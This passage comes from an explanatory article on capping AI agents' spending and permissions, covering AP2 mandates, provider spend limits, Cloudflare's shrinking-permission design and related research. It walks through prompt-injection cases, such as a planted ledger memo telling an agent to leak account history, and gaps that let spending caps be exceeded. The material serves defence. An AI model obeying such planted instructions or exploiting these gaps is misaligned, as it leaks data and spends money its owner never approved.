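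Splitting the budget also avoids the shared counter. In *Concordat* (2026), a software library for agents, an agent that delegates work gives up part of its own budget. If an agent with $10 gives a sub-agent $4, it keeps $6, and the two can then work in parallel without overspending. However, the sub-agent may finish with $3 unspent while the first agent runs out. An early version accepted negative amounts, so an agent with $10 could give a sub-agent −$4 and end up with $14. The developers fixed this in the next version, but any counter of this kind must reject negative amounts.

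A blockchain wallet's balance avoids this problem because the blockchain never transfers more than the wallet holds. If the agent signs too many payments at once, the later ones fail. This is another reason to keep the balance small, even when a policy rule sets a daily cap.

### Prices that are known only afterwards

Companies that sell access to language models usually charge by the token, a short piece of text unrelated to an access token. The price of a request isn't known in advance because the length of the model's answer isn't known. A counter can reserve the price of the longest permitted answer. At $5 per million input tokens and $25 per million output tokens, a request with 10,000 input tokens and at most 4,000 output tokens can cost up to $0.15, so the counter reserves that amount. If the answer has only 400 tokens, the request costs $0.06, and the counter releases the remaining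 $0.09.

However, reserved money isn't available to other calls. Khan's simplest method reserved four to six times the actual cost. If a call costs $1 but the counter reserves $5, only two calls can run at once on a remaining budget of $10, although ten would fit. A method that learned from earlier calls reserved about twice the actual cost. Using the provider's token counter brought the reserved amount close to the actual cost but delayed each call by 0.9 to 1.7 seconds.

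Some models also produce hidden reasoning before they answer, and providers charge for it. Khan warns that the limit on output tokens may not cover this reasoning, so the cost can exceed the reservation. For such models, Khan recommends relying first on the provider's controls over reasoning.

Anthropic's gateway checks a developer's total before each request and adds the cost after the response, without reserving any of the budget in between. The last request can therefore exceed the cap, and if 50 requests start while a few cents remain, all 50 can pass. Anthropic gives the same explanation on a support page for customers who went over their limit. An operator can allow for this by lowering the cap by the number of parallel requests times the highest likely price per request.

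If the gateway doesn't recognize a model, it charges a default rate instead of nothing. If a program cuts off an answer before the final count arrives, the gateway estimates the cost of the text already sent, so an agent can't avoid the cap by disconnecting early. But if the gateway can't reach its database within two seconds, it lets the request through by default. Anthropic offers a setting that refuses requests instead, which is usually better for an unattended agent.

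The gateway's cap for an organization applies to each developer separately, so a monthly cap of $500 lets 40 developers spend $20,000 a month in total.

On a blockchain, a wallet can approve a contract to withdraw up to a stated amount later. Circle counts the full amount when the agent submits the approval, so approving $80 for a $30 purchase uses $80 of the agent's daily cap. This overstates the spending, but it is safe because the contract can withdraw the other $50 later without going through Circle. The agent should approve only what the purchase requires.

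The same gap affects approvals granted before the operator set any limits. Circle's rules don't cancel them, so a contract can still use them without any check. An operator should revoke old approvals before relying on a new cap. A contract allowlist that includes USDC also lets the agent approve withdrawals by anyone, because the list checks only which contract the agent calls, not who may withdraw the money. Limiting those approvals takes a separate rule on recipients.

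### Whether model providers' budgets stop requests

A model provider's budget may stop requests or only send an email, and OpenAI's *Spend limits* describes both. A spend alert sends a notification and lets requests continue. To stop them, a customer has to enter a monthly limit for the organization or a project and turn on "Enforce a hard limit". Once spending reaches that limit, OpenAI refuses requests with status 429 until the next monthly cycle, unless the customer raises the limit. Spending can go slightly over because the block takes a little time to take effect.

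Older advice about OpenAI's limits is unreliable because the rules have changed at least twice. In May 2024, Willison (2024), a programmer who writes about AI tools, welcomed a project limit that rejected requests once it was reached. A later reply in the forum thread *How to Set Billing Limits and Restrict Model Usage for a Project* quotes OpenAI as calling the monthly budget a soft threshold that does not interrupt requests. A company that set its limit under either rule should check what the limit does now.

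Anthropic blocks requests once a customer reaches a spending limit. Anthropic's *Rate limits* lists monthly caps from $500 to $200,000, depending on the class of customer, and customers can set a lower limit for their organization or for a workspace within it. Anthropic normally returns status 400 when a customer reaches its own limit and 429 when it reaches Anthropic's cap. Many programs respond to a 429 by waiting briefly and retrying, which doesn't help when the cap has been reached, because access returns only at the start of the next month or when Anthropic grants a higher limit. The runtime should therefore read the detailed error code and stop the agent.

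A spending limit on Anthropic's default workspace may not cover some usage, including sessions of Claude Managed Agents, Anthropic's service for running agents. The organization's limit covers all of it. A company that wants to cap one agent's spending should therefore run it in a separate workspace.

Google's monthly caps for projects that use its Gemini models take effect after a delay of about ten minutes, and the customer pays for any usage during the delay, according to Google's *Giving you more transparency and control over your Gemini API costs*. Agents spending $6 a minute together would exceed the cap by about $60. Google Cloud's *Manage spend cap budgets* describes a cap that blocks the service until the next budget period, which usually begins on the first of the month.

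All these limits are monthly. An agent that gets stuck in a loop on the second night of the month can spend the whole month's allowance by morning, and the company's other agents may stop working as a result. A company that wants a daily cap has to track the spending itself or use a gateway.

### What the user signs under AP2

A wallet cap limits how much an agent spends but not what it buys. The Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) is meant to limit both. Google announced it in September 2025 and has since donated it to the FIDO Alliance, an industry group that develops login standards. The *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation* assumes that nobody can reliably prevent prompt injection and therefore treats every agent as a potential attacker.

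The protocol's basic document is the mandate, a digitally signed record of what an agent may do. A checkout mandate covers the goods, and a payment mandate covers the payment. A user who is present approves the final purchase directly. Otherwise, the user approves an open mandate in advance, which sets conditions for later purchases, and the agent then produces a closed mandate for each one.

Suppose the shop's owner wants the agent to buy packaging during the coming year. The agent drafts the open mandates, and the owner reads and approves them on a screen that no language model controls, which AP2 calls the trusted surface. The trusted surface signs the mandates with the owner's key or, in another version of the scheme, with the key of the company behind the agent. Each open mandate also names the agent's key, so a thief who copies the mandate can't use it.

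AP2's *Payment Mandate* defines the conditions. The shop's owner could choose these:

| Condition | Value | Check for each purchase |
|---|---|---|
| Amount range | At most $120 | The price is within the range |
| Budget | $600 | This purchase plus all earlier ones costs at most $600 |
| Allowed payees | Two packaging suppliers | The seller is on the list |
| Execution date | During 2027 | The payment date is within the year |
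| Recurrence | Monthly, at most 12 times | Enough time has passed, and the count is within the limit |

The amount range works as a per-call cap. The budget is a total for the whole mandate, so it never resets. In this example, the agent can make five purchases of $120, and the sixth fails although the mandate allows twelve. Without the budget, the agent could spend $1,440.

AP2 has no dedicated daily or monthly cap, but the recurrence condition can serve the same purpose. It measures the time since the agent last used the mandate. Under `MONTHLY`, an agent that makes a purchase on January 31 therefore shouldn't be able to make another on February 1, although a calendar cap would allow it. If the owner chooses `ON_DEMAND` instead, the agent doesn't have to wait and can spend the $600 within minutes.

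When the agent finds suitable boxes for $110, the supplier signs a description of the order. The agent signs a closed checkout mandate and a closed payment mandate, both tied to this order. It sends the open and closed payment mandates to the credential provider, the company that supplies the means of payment, such as a digital wallet. If the purchase meets the conditions, the credential provider returns a payment credential. The agent passes this credential to the supplier with the checkout mandates, and the supplier checks that the goods match what the owner approved. The supplier's payment processor then checks that the credential belongs to this order.

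AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* requires ordinary code to make these checks, even if a company uses a language model to communicate with agents. A condition that the company doesn't recognize counts as failed. The company can then ask the user to approve the purchase directly, so a new kind of condition may delay the purchase but doesn't weaken the mandate.

The unit of money is less clear. The amount range requires whole cents, but the example beside it gives a maximum of 100.50. The budget has no stated unit, and its example is 1000.00, while payment amounts are in cents. If the shop writes a $600 budget as 600.00 and the credential provider reads it as cents, the budget becomes $6. If the shop writes it as 60000 and the provider reads it as dollars, the budget becomes $60,000. The agent's normal purchases would not reveal the second mistake, but a test purchase just above $600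 would.

### Who keeps the running total

The budget works only if somebody adds up the purchases. AP2 requires a running total but doesn't specify who keeps it. Under its rules for checking mandates, the credential provider and, where there is one, the payment network must check every condition in the open payment mandate, so they need the total. The supplier can't keep the total because it normally receives only the checkout mandates.

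The agent also must not sign a second purchase under the same open mandate until it has a receipt that rejects the first. Taken literally, this rule forbids the repeat purchases that the recurrence condition allows, so the specification needs some revision. Under AP2, the part of the agent that signs mandates should run ordinary code, and the receipts should be kept where the model can't alter them. But AP2 treats the agent as a potential attacker, so it can't rely on the agent's own records. The credential provider, network and payment processor may reject overlapping purchases, but AP2 doesn't require them to.

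An agent that uses two credential providers can exceed its spending cap even if both providers follow the rules. Suppose the owner's mandate lets the agent pay with a card from one provider or a bank transfer through another. Each provider adds up only the purchases it handles, and AP2 describes no way for them to share a total. The agent could spend $600 through each, for a total of $1,200. The owner can prevent this by using another AP2 condition to allow only one means of payment.

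Software that checks mandates may not keep a running total of spending. According to its documentation, Farigate, which offers a checkpoint for agents' actions, records AP2's budget and recurrence conditions but doesn't yet enforce them across purchases. Under AP2's rules, a credential provider that can't check a condition should return an `unresolved_constraint` error, and the user can then step in. Before relying on a budget, the shop should ask its credential provider whether it keeps a total, then test this with two purchases that together exceed the limit.

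### A wallet's own limit and a check by others

A limit in a wallet is easier to enforce because the wallet has to sign every payment. One company tracks the spending, and the seller doesn't need to know about the limit. The owner can also lower the limit at any time, whereas a signed open mandate under AP2 may stay valid until it expires. AP2 recommends the shortest practical lifetime, and its sample mandate lasts one hour, but a mandate for monthly purchases has to last much longer.

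A wallet has little information about what the agent is buying. It can't distinguish a $60 payment to an approved supplier for the right part from one for the wrong part. AP2's checkout mandate can list the acceptable items and quantities, and the supplier has to compare them with the order. The signed mandates also give both sides evidence in a dispute, whereas a wallet's record shows only that the payment took place. But the supplier profits from the sale, so it is poorly placed to protect the owner's interests. A check by the credential provider is more convincing if the provider and supplier are separate companies, but AP2 allows one company to take on several or all of the roles.

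Neither method prevents a bad purchase within the limits. If an attacker's message persuades the agent to pay $119 for boxes worth $40, the payment is still allowed because it is below the $120 cap. According to its documentation, AP2 is meant to limit the loss, since an agent may choose badly.

The two methods work well together because AP2 allows a digital wallet to act as the credential provider. The wallet can check the mandate's conditions and apply its own daily cap before releasing money. In one of AP2's published examples, an agent pays through x402 while the user is away. For the shop's packaging, the owner could sign the mandate described above and set the wallet's daily cap at $120. If faulty software ignored the monthly recurrence, the agent could still make only one $120 purchase a day, and the owner would have a chance to notice before it spent the whole $600.

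## Permissions that shrink during a task: Cloudflare's Agent Access Model

A period cap stops a series of payments that a per-call cap would allow one by one. Most rules on data have no equivalent way to limit what a series of calls does in total. Suppose the shop's allowlist reasonably lets an agent read the ledger and open support cases with the payment processor. If someone plants an instruction in the ledger to attach the account history to a support case, the agent can send the shop's accounts to an outside company without breaking any rule.

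*AgentGuardian* (2026) describes a similar attack, in which an agent exports sensitive data to a temporary file and then emails the file. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) cites a reported case on GitHub in which a malicious instruction in a public repository led an agent to read its user's private repositories and publish them. The danger came from combining private data, text written by strangers and a way to send data out, and checking each call separately can't detect that combination.

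A fixed allowlist handles this badly. The agent needs both rules to do its job, but keeping both in place throughout the task makes the leak possible. The agent can leak the ledger through the support operation only after reading it, so the right set of rules depends on what the agent has already done. Some of Dogwood's temporal conditions can express this dependence for calls through one gateway.

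The network company Cloudflare proposed a more general answer in August 2026. Silverlock's *The Agent Access Model* describes a reference architecture in which an agent starts with the permissions for one task and loses some of them when it reads protected data. Silverlock gives no measurements of how well it works.

### From a task template to a frozen request

The design gives each run of a task its own permissions. A run lasts from the start of the task to its end and includes the work of any sub-agents. A job repeated the next night counts as a new run.

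The permissions come from a task template, which a person or an authorized system writes in advance. A template might let a reconciliation job read three tables and post to one channel. The company needs one template for each kind of task, however often the task runs. The agent has no part in writing the template, so a planted message can't widen the permissions it grants.

When a run starts, an access engine compares the template with what the person who started the run may do and what the agent's service may do. It then applies the rules of the data's owners and the organization. The run can only ever make requests that all four sources permit. For example, an administrator who can delete customers may start the reconciliation job, but the run still can't delete customers because the template doesn't list that operation. A junior employee also can't use a broad template to read a table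 that is closed to junior employees.

The run then receives a token that expires when the task ends or earlier. The token is tied to a cryptographic key that the runtime holds and the model never receives, so someone who finds the token in a file can't use it without the key. If the token in PocketOS's file had been of this kind, the agent could not have used it to delete the volume, but Railway would first have had to support such tokens.

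DPoP, the standard that ties a token to a key, adds a proof to each request that covers the HTTP method and the address, but not the query string or the body. On Railway's GraphQL API, the proof would therefore be the same for a harmless query and a deletion.

The design freezes each request before checking it. An adapter records the complete request, including the operation, the resource, the recipient and any arguments that affect its scope. The access engine checks this copy, and the adapter then executes the same copy. Without this step, a program could check a refund of $38 and then send a request for $3,800 because the amount field had changed after the check.

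### Closing the exits before the data arrives

Cloudflare calls the part that removes permissions the Trust Ratchet, after the tool that turns in only one direction. A policy lists in advance which events trigger it and what each event removes. When the agent makes a permitted read that returns protected data, the following happens:

1. The runtime receives the response but withholds it from the model.
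2. A central store records a new, narrower set of permissions for the run.
3. Each enforcement point stops using the old permissions, clears any decisions it has cached, and confirms the change. The runtime cancels or finishes calls already in progress, and the network proxy closes or rechecks open connections.
4. Once every enforcement point has confirmed, the runtime passes the response to the model.

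The order matters because an agent can read a table and send it out within seconds. If the model received the data at step 1, it could use the old permissions until the enforcement points applied the new ones. Open connections need the same care, since one that the proxy approved earlier could carry the data later.

The set of requests a run may make can shrink but never grow (Aₜ₊₁ ⊆ Aₜ, where Aₜ is the set allowed after step t). Neither renewing the credential nor getting a person's approval restores a removed permission. Work that needs that permission has to start as a new run with its own authorization.

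Cloudflare's design requires data passed to a new run to keep its classification, so that an agent can't get around the ratchet by taking protected data into a new run with full permissions. The new run starts in the restricted state, and can start with more permissions only if an authorized step has produced a less sensitive version of the data. Restored memory also counts as an input, and a run whose inputs nobody has classified starts restricted or doesn't start at all. Parkinson and colleagues reach the same conclusion for their own design, in which starting a new session achieves nothing if it picks up the same sensitive data.

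### The nightly reconciliation job

Silverlock gives the example of a finance team's agent that runs every night. It fetches a settlement report from a payment processor, compares it with two ledgers, and posts a short summary to the team's channel. It can also contact vendor support about certain exceptions. When the run starts, the agent gets at most ten minutes and permission for only these operations, with the recipient already fixed.

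The agent fetches the settlement report first. The policy classifies the report as protected, so the runtime withholds it until the ratchet has closed two of the five paths.

| Path | At the start | Once the agent has the report |
|---|---|---|
| Processor's report API | Open | Closed |
| Vendor support | Open | Closed |
| First ledger (read) | Open | Open |
| Second ledger (read) | Open | Open |
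| Summary to the finance channel | Open | Open |

The agent then reads the ledgers. A memo in one of them contains a planted instruction to attach the full account history to a support case with the processor. The agent tries, but the runtime blocks the call, which was permitted a few minutes earlier. A direct connection to the processor also fails because the network proxy has closed that path.

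A free-text summary could contain the ledger, so the agent instead submits a structured result with a status and some totals. An adapter checks the result against a schema that has a size limit and no free-text field, stores it, and gives the agent an identifier. To post the summary, the agent can supply only that identifier, and the adapter sends the stored result to the finance channel. The agent could still put other information in a number field, such as an account number in place of a total, but it would reach only the finance team.

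The example also shows that the ratchet can block useful requests. The agent loses access to support as soon as it receives the report, before it has compared anything. It could ask support about a report that never arrived, but not about a mismatch between the report and a ledger, which seems a more likely reason to contact a processor. To report a mismatch, the company would need a second run that receives only a cleaned-up version of the finding, such as a transaction number. The agent also can't fetch the report again if the first copy is incomplete.

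### What the restrictions cost

Silverlock concedes that a broad ratchet policy refuses harmless work along with attacks, especially while the classifications are coarse. The nearest measurements are in *Bounded Agents* (Muruaga, 2026). Muruaga built a system that checks each call against the earlier calls in the session. Its rules forbid pairs of actions, such as reading a confidential document and then sending an external message. They can also forbid longer sequences, which catches an agent that copies the data to a file between those two steps.

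Muruaga assumed that an attacker controlled the model and inserted the attacker's tool call directly after the agent's first legitimate one. On AgentDojo, the benchmark used to test Progent, between 75% and 100% of attempts to send data out succeeded without the system, depending on the domain, and none succeeded with it. Across 949 test cases, the system also reduced the share of user tasks the agent completed, by 8.6 percentage points when a simulated person approved the calls that needed approval and by 13.9 points when nobody did. In the banking tests, completion fell from 68.8% to 50.0% when nobody approved calls. These losses come from all of the system's checks together, so rules on combinations alone may reduce completion less.

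The protection also depends on a complete list of forbidden pairs. On InjecAgent, another benchmark, the full list blocked all 544 attempts to steal data, but 39.9% got through after Muruaga removed a single pair. Blocklists usually have this weakness. Cloudflare's ratchet is less exposed to it because the restricted state can list the few paths that stay open and refuse everything else. But somebody still has to mark the right data as protected. If nobody had classified the settlement report, fetching it would not have reduced the agent's permissions.

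Rules on combinations do little against an attack that needs only one permitted call. On InjecAgent, 60.4% of direct-harm attacks still succeeded, and stopping them requires checks on argument values like those in Progent. Muruaga also compared the two systems on AgentDojo, with hand-written rules for Progent. No attack succeeded against either, and the agents completed similar shares of their tasks in the two domains with reported figures. A record of earlier calls may therefore add little where somebody can write exact argument rules. It should help more when the agent needs a fairly open tool, such as general email.

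Parkinson and colleagues describe a gentler design, in which an agent can acquire permissions during a task, within limits its owner has set. Each permission expires, and it uses up a budget while the agent holds it. The rate of use rises as the session approaches a forbidden combination of three properties: exposure to untrusted text, access to sensitive data, and a way to send data out or change something. If the session has a share φ of these properties, the rate is multiplied by 1/(1 − φ), which is 1.5 for one property and 3 for two. The system refuses any permission that would add the third, however much of the budget is left.

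The properties stay with the session after the permissions expire. In a simulation with made-up parameters, a hijacked agent gains read access to eight private repositories, and the system blocks it from publishing through a public one. The budget then runs out and all eight permissions lapse. When the agent tries to publish again, the system still blocks it, because what the agent has read remains in its context. This design also blocks legitimate work, such as moving private code to a public repository, unless the owner approves an exception or a trusted step cleans the code first.

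A second drawback of Cloudflare's design is its dependence on a shared control system. The runtime and the network proxy are separate so that a fault in one doesn't open the other, but both rely on the same task policy and the same record of what the ratchet has removed. The shared system has to fail closed, meaning that any error or missing confirmation blocks the response. If five components each confirm 99.9% of the time, independently, about one transition in 200 fails (1 − 0.999⁵). That is tolerable for a nightly job, which someone can rerun in the morning, but it may not be for a customer waiting in a chat. An outage of the shared system would stop every run that needs protected data.

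The controls also don't monitor encrypted traffic or the connections that a remote tool server makes, which are outside the control of the company's proxy. Even on monitored paths, the design can't prevent a leak through an approved destination that an attacker has taken over, or through an output schema that permits too much.

### Revising the allowlist from the log

People who write permission templates have to guess what a task needs, and they tend to overestimate to avoid complaints. Parkinson and colleagues cite one vendor's analysis, which found that accounts on several cloud platforms used only 1% of their permissions. Cloudflare's design corrects the templates using a log of what each run did and what the enforcement points refused. The enforcement points produce the log entries, because a planted message can influence the model's own account of its actions.

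A review process checks the log and proposes removing any permission that has gone unused across many successful runs. If the same refusal recurs in failed runs, the process may propose adding the refused permission, but only when the task's definition and the resource's owner support the request. A person decides on each proposal, and changes apply only to future runs.

Repeated refusals are weak evidence that an agent lacks a permission it needs, because an attacker can cause them. Suppose an attacker plants an order note instructing the shop's support agent to download the customer list, and the agent tries 200 times. The log then shows 200 refusals, which look like a missing permission. Counting affected runs instead of requests helps, because 200 attempts in one run count once, but the attacker can plant the note in an order that the agent reads every day. The reviewer therefore has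 to check whether the job requires the customer list, which it doesn't for a support agent that looks up one order at a time.

In the design by Parkinson and colleagues, a permission that an agent has borrowed in enough of its recent tasks becomes a candidate for its permanent set. They caution that frequent use shows only that the agent needs the permission, not that it is safe for the agent to hold it all the time. They also warn that a series of individually reasonable additions can produce an overbroad list.

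Removing unused permissions has its own risk, because some exist for rare emergencies. If a job needs a recovery operation in one run out of 1,000, the chance that 200 runs will pass without it is 82% (0.999²⁰⁰). That chance falls to 5% over about 3,000 runs, which would take a nightly job more than eight years. The reviewer can't tell from the log in a reasonable time whether such a permission is needed, so they have to know what it is for. The company could keep the permission in a separate template for recovery work and remove it from the ordinary job.

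### Google's Beyond Zero

Google's approach examines each request more closely. *Beyond Zero* (Valente and Zalewski, 2026) describes an architecture for employees and agents that decides whether to allow each action instead of granting access to whole applications. Fixed rules set a minimum that always applies, and a reasoning engine also takes into account who is asking, what they are working on, how sensitive the data is, and what they did before and after the request.

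The engine can allow a request, deny it or issue a challenge. A challenge might require a person to explain the request, touch a security key or get a manager's approval. If the risk looks serious, the system can also withdraw some or all of the person's access, sometimes until the security team has interviewed them. Access decisions leave little time for reasoning, so AI models prepare much of the information beforehand, for example by classifying documents and extracting work assignments. Slower investigations, which take minutes, run in parallel.

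In Google's example, an agent called SalesGenie is allowed to read sales reports but queries a confidential strategy document. The agent's user works on financial services accounts in one region, and a policy requires users to have a work assignment that matches any document this sensitive. The system asks the user to confirm the request and then to get approval from the team that owns the document. When the user fails these challenges and a closer review of recent activity suggests theft, the system cuts off the user's access.

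A Cloudflare template that listed the sales reports would have blocked the same query immediately, without any reasoning. The example is therefore better evidence against giving agents broad access to applications than it is for using a reasoning engine.

Beyond Zero is best suited to work whose access needs nobody can list in advance. An analyst's assistant may need different documents every day, and a template wide enough to cover them all would protect very little. A reasoning engine can allow ordinary requests, question unusual ones, and still give access to somebody with a good reason. It can also detect patterns across applications and weeks, such as an employee opening 500% more files than colleagues in the same job. Cloudflare's ratchet can't make that comparison because it starts afresh with each run.

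Cloudflare's approach works best for jobs like the nightly reconciliation, which need the same few operations every time. An operator can list what the agent may do in each state and test those rules before the first run. The agent's permissions then don't depend on a model's judgment. This matters because an attacker who can plant text for the agent may also influence a model that reads the agent's plans to infer its intent. A slow investigation can limit further damage but can't recover data that has already leaked.

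Silverlock points out that the two approaches can work together, since a smaller set of permissions leaves the reasoning engine with less to judge. Both depend on correct labels for sensitive data. Neither company has published figures that allow a comparison. *Going Beyond Zero* (Adkins and Ramamoorthy, 2026) says that early prototypes and deployments inside Google are improving detection of access abuse, but it doesn't say by how much.

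### Limits on combined actions remain the largest gap

In September 2026, Surapani and colleagues compared ten families of security mechanisms with seven requirements for authorizing agents. The only requirement that no family met even substantially was a limit on what an agent can do or learn by combining permitted calls. Information-flow control, which tracks where data may go, and provenance records, which document where it came from, each met it partially. The other eight families didn't address it, and neither did any of the three complete set-ups the team examined, which included Amazon's Bedrock Agents and MCP servers with OAuth.

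The ratings cover only the literature reviewed, and other work from 2026 narrows the gap. Muruaga's system blocks forbidden combinations within a session. *RATION* (2026) limits quantities that add up over a whole task, such as the number of calls that change something. *AIRGuard* (2026) derives each step's permissions from the task's, so they can only narrow, and keeps a history of actions to judge sequences. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) surveys several systems that track individual values, including CaMeL, which records the data each value came from and checks this when the agent makes a call. In principle, such a system could let the reconciliation agent send support a harmless question after reading the ledger, whereas the ratchet blocks every message to support.

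All of these systems control actions or the movement of data. Surapani and colleagues also consider what an agent can infer from data it is allowed to read. Suppose an agent may request average salaries but not individual ones. If the average for ten employees is $50,000 and the average for the nine other than Ann is $48,000, Ann earns $68,000 (500,000 − 432,000). Both requests are permitted, and a colleague could learn her salary without any data leaving the company. Database researchers have studied this problem for decades, but their remedies assume statistical queries on a fixed set of data. An agent can combine calendars, emails and contact lists, and nobody has a general method for calculating what they reveal together.

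### What a company can build today

Existing standards and products cover much of Cloudflare's design, but not the ratchet.

| Part of the design | State in 2026 |
|---|---|
| Credential for one task | OAuth standards support short-lived, narrowed tokens tied to a key |
| Checks on tool calls and arguments | Available, but MCP leaves the rules to the operator |
| Control of outgoing connections | Available in proxies such as OpenShell's |
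| Ratchet shared by the runtime and the network | No standard, so a company has to build it |
| Activity log | Standard formats exist, but not a shared set of fields for agents |
| One agent serving people with different permissions | Unsolved from end to end |

Support for narrow credentials still varies by API. GitHub can give an app a token that expires after an hour and works only for named repositories and permissions, according to Parkinson and colleagues. Railway's tokens could not be limited to managing domains.

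A small company can build a simple ratchet if an agent can make calls only through one gateway. The gateway can set a flag for the run before it returns protected data, then allow only calls on a shorter list. Using a single gateway avoids the difficult part of Cloudflare's version, which is keeping several enforcement points in sync. The gateway still has to handle calls already in progress. It also has to apply the flag to any sub-agents, or one agent could read the ledger and another could send it.

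The last row of the table is the hardest case. Suppose Alice may see the shop's revenue and Bob may not, and both use the same agent in a shared channel. If the agent has read the figures to answer Alice, its next answer to Bob may reveal them. Restricting the agent to data both may see prevents the leak but makes it less useful to Alice. Reusing a stored answer for somebody else causes the same problem. Silverlock suggests labeling each piece of data with the permissions under which the agent obtained it and checking the labels before every answer, but knows of no widely deployed system that does this from end to end. For now, Cloudflare's model assumes that a run acts with one set of permissions, fixed before it starts.

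Silverlock advises starting with one agent that has a narrow job and touches important records, such as the nightly reconciliation. The company replaces the agent's permanent key with a credential for each task, sends the agent's tool calls and network traffic through enforcement points, and turns on the log. The log shows which permissions the job uses, so the company can narrow the template accordingly.
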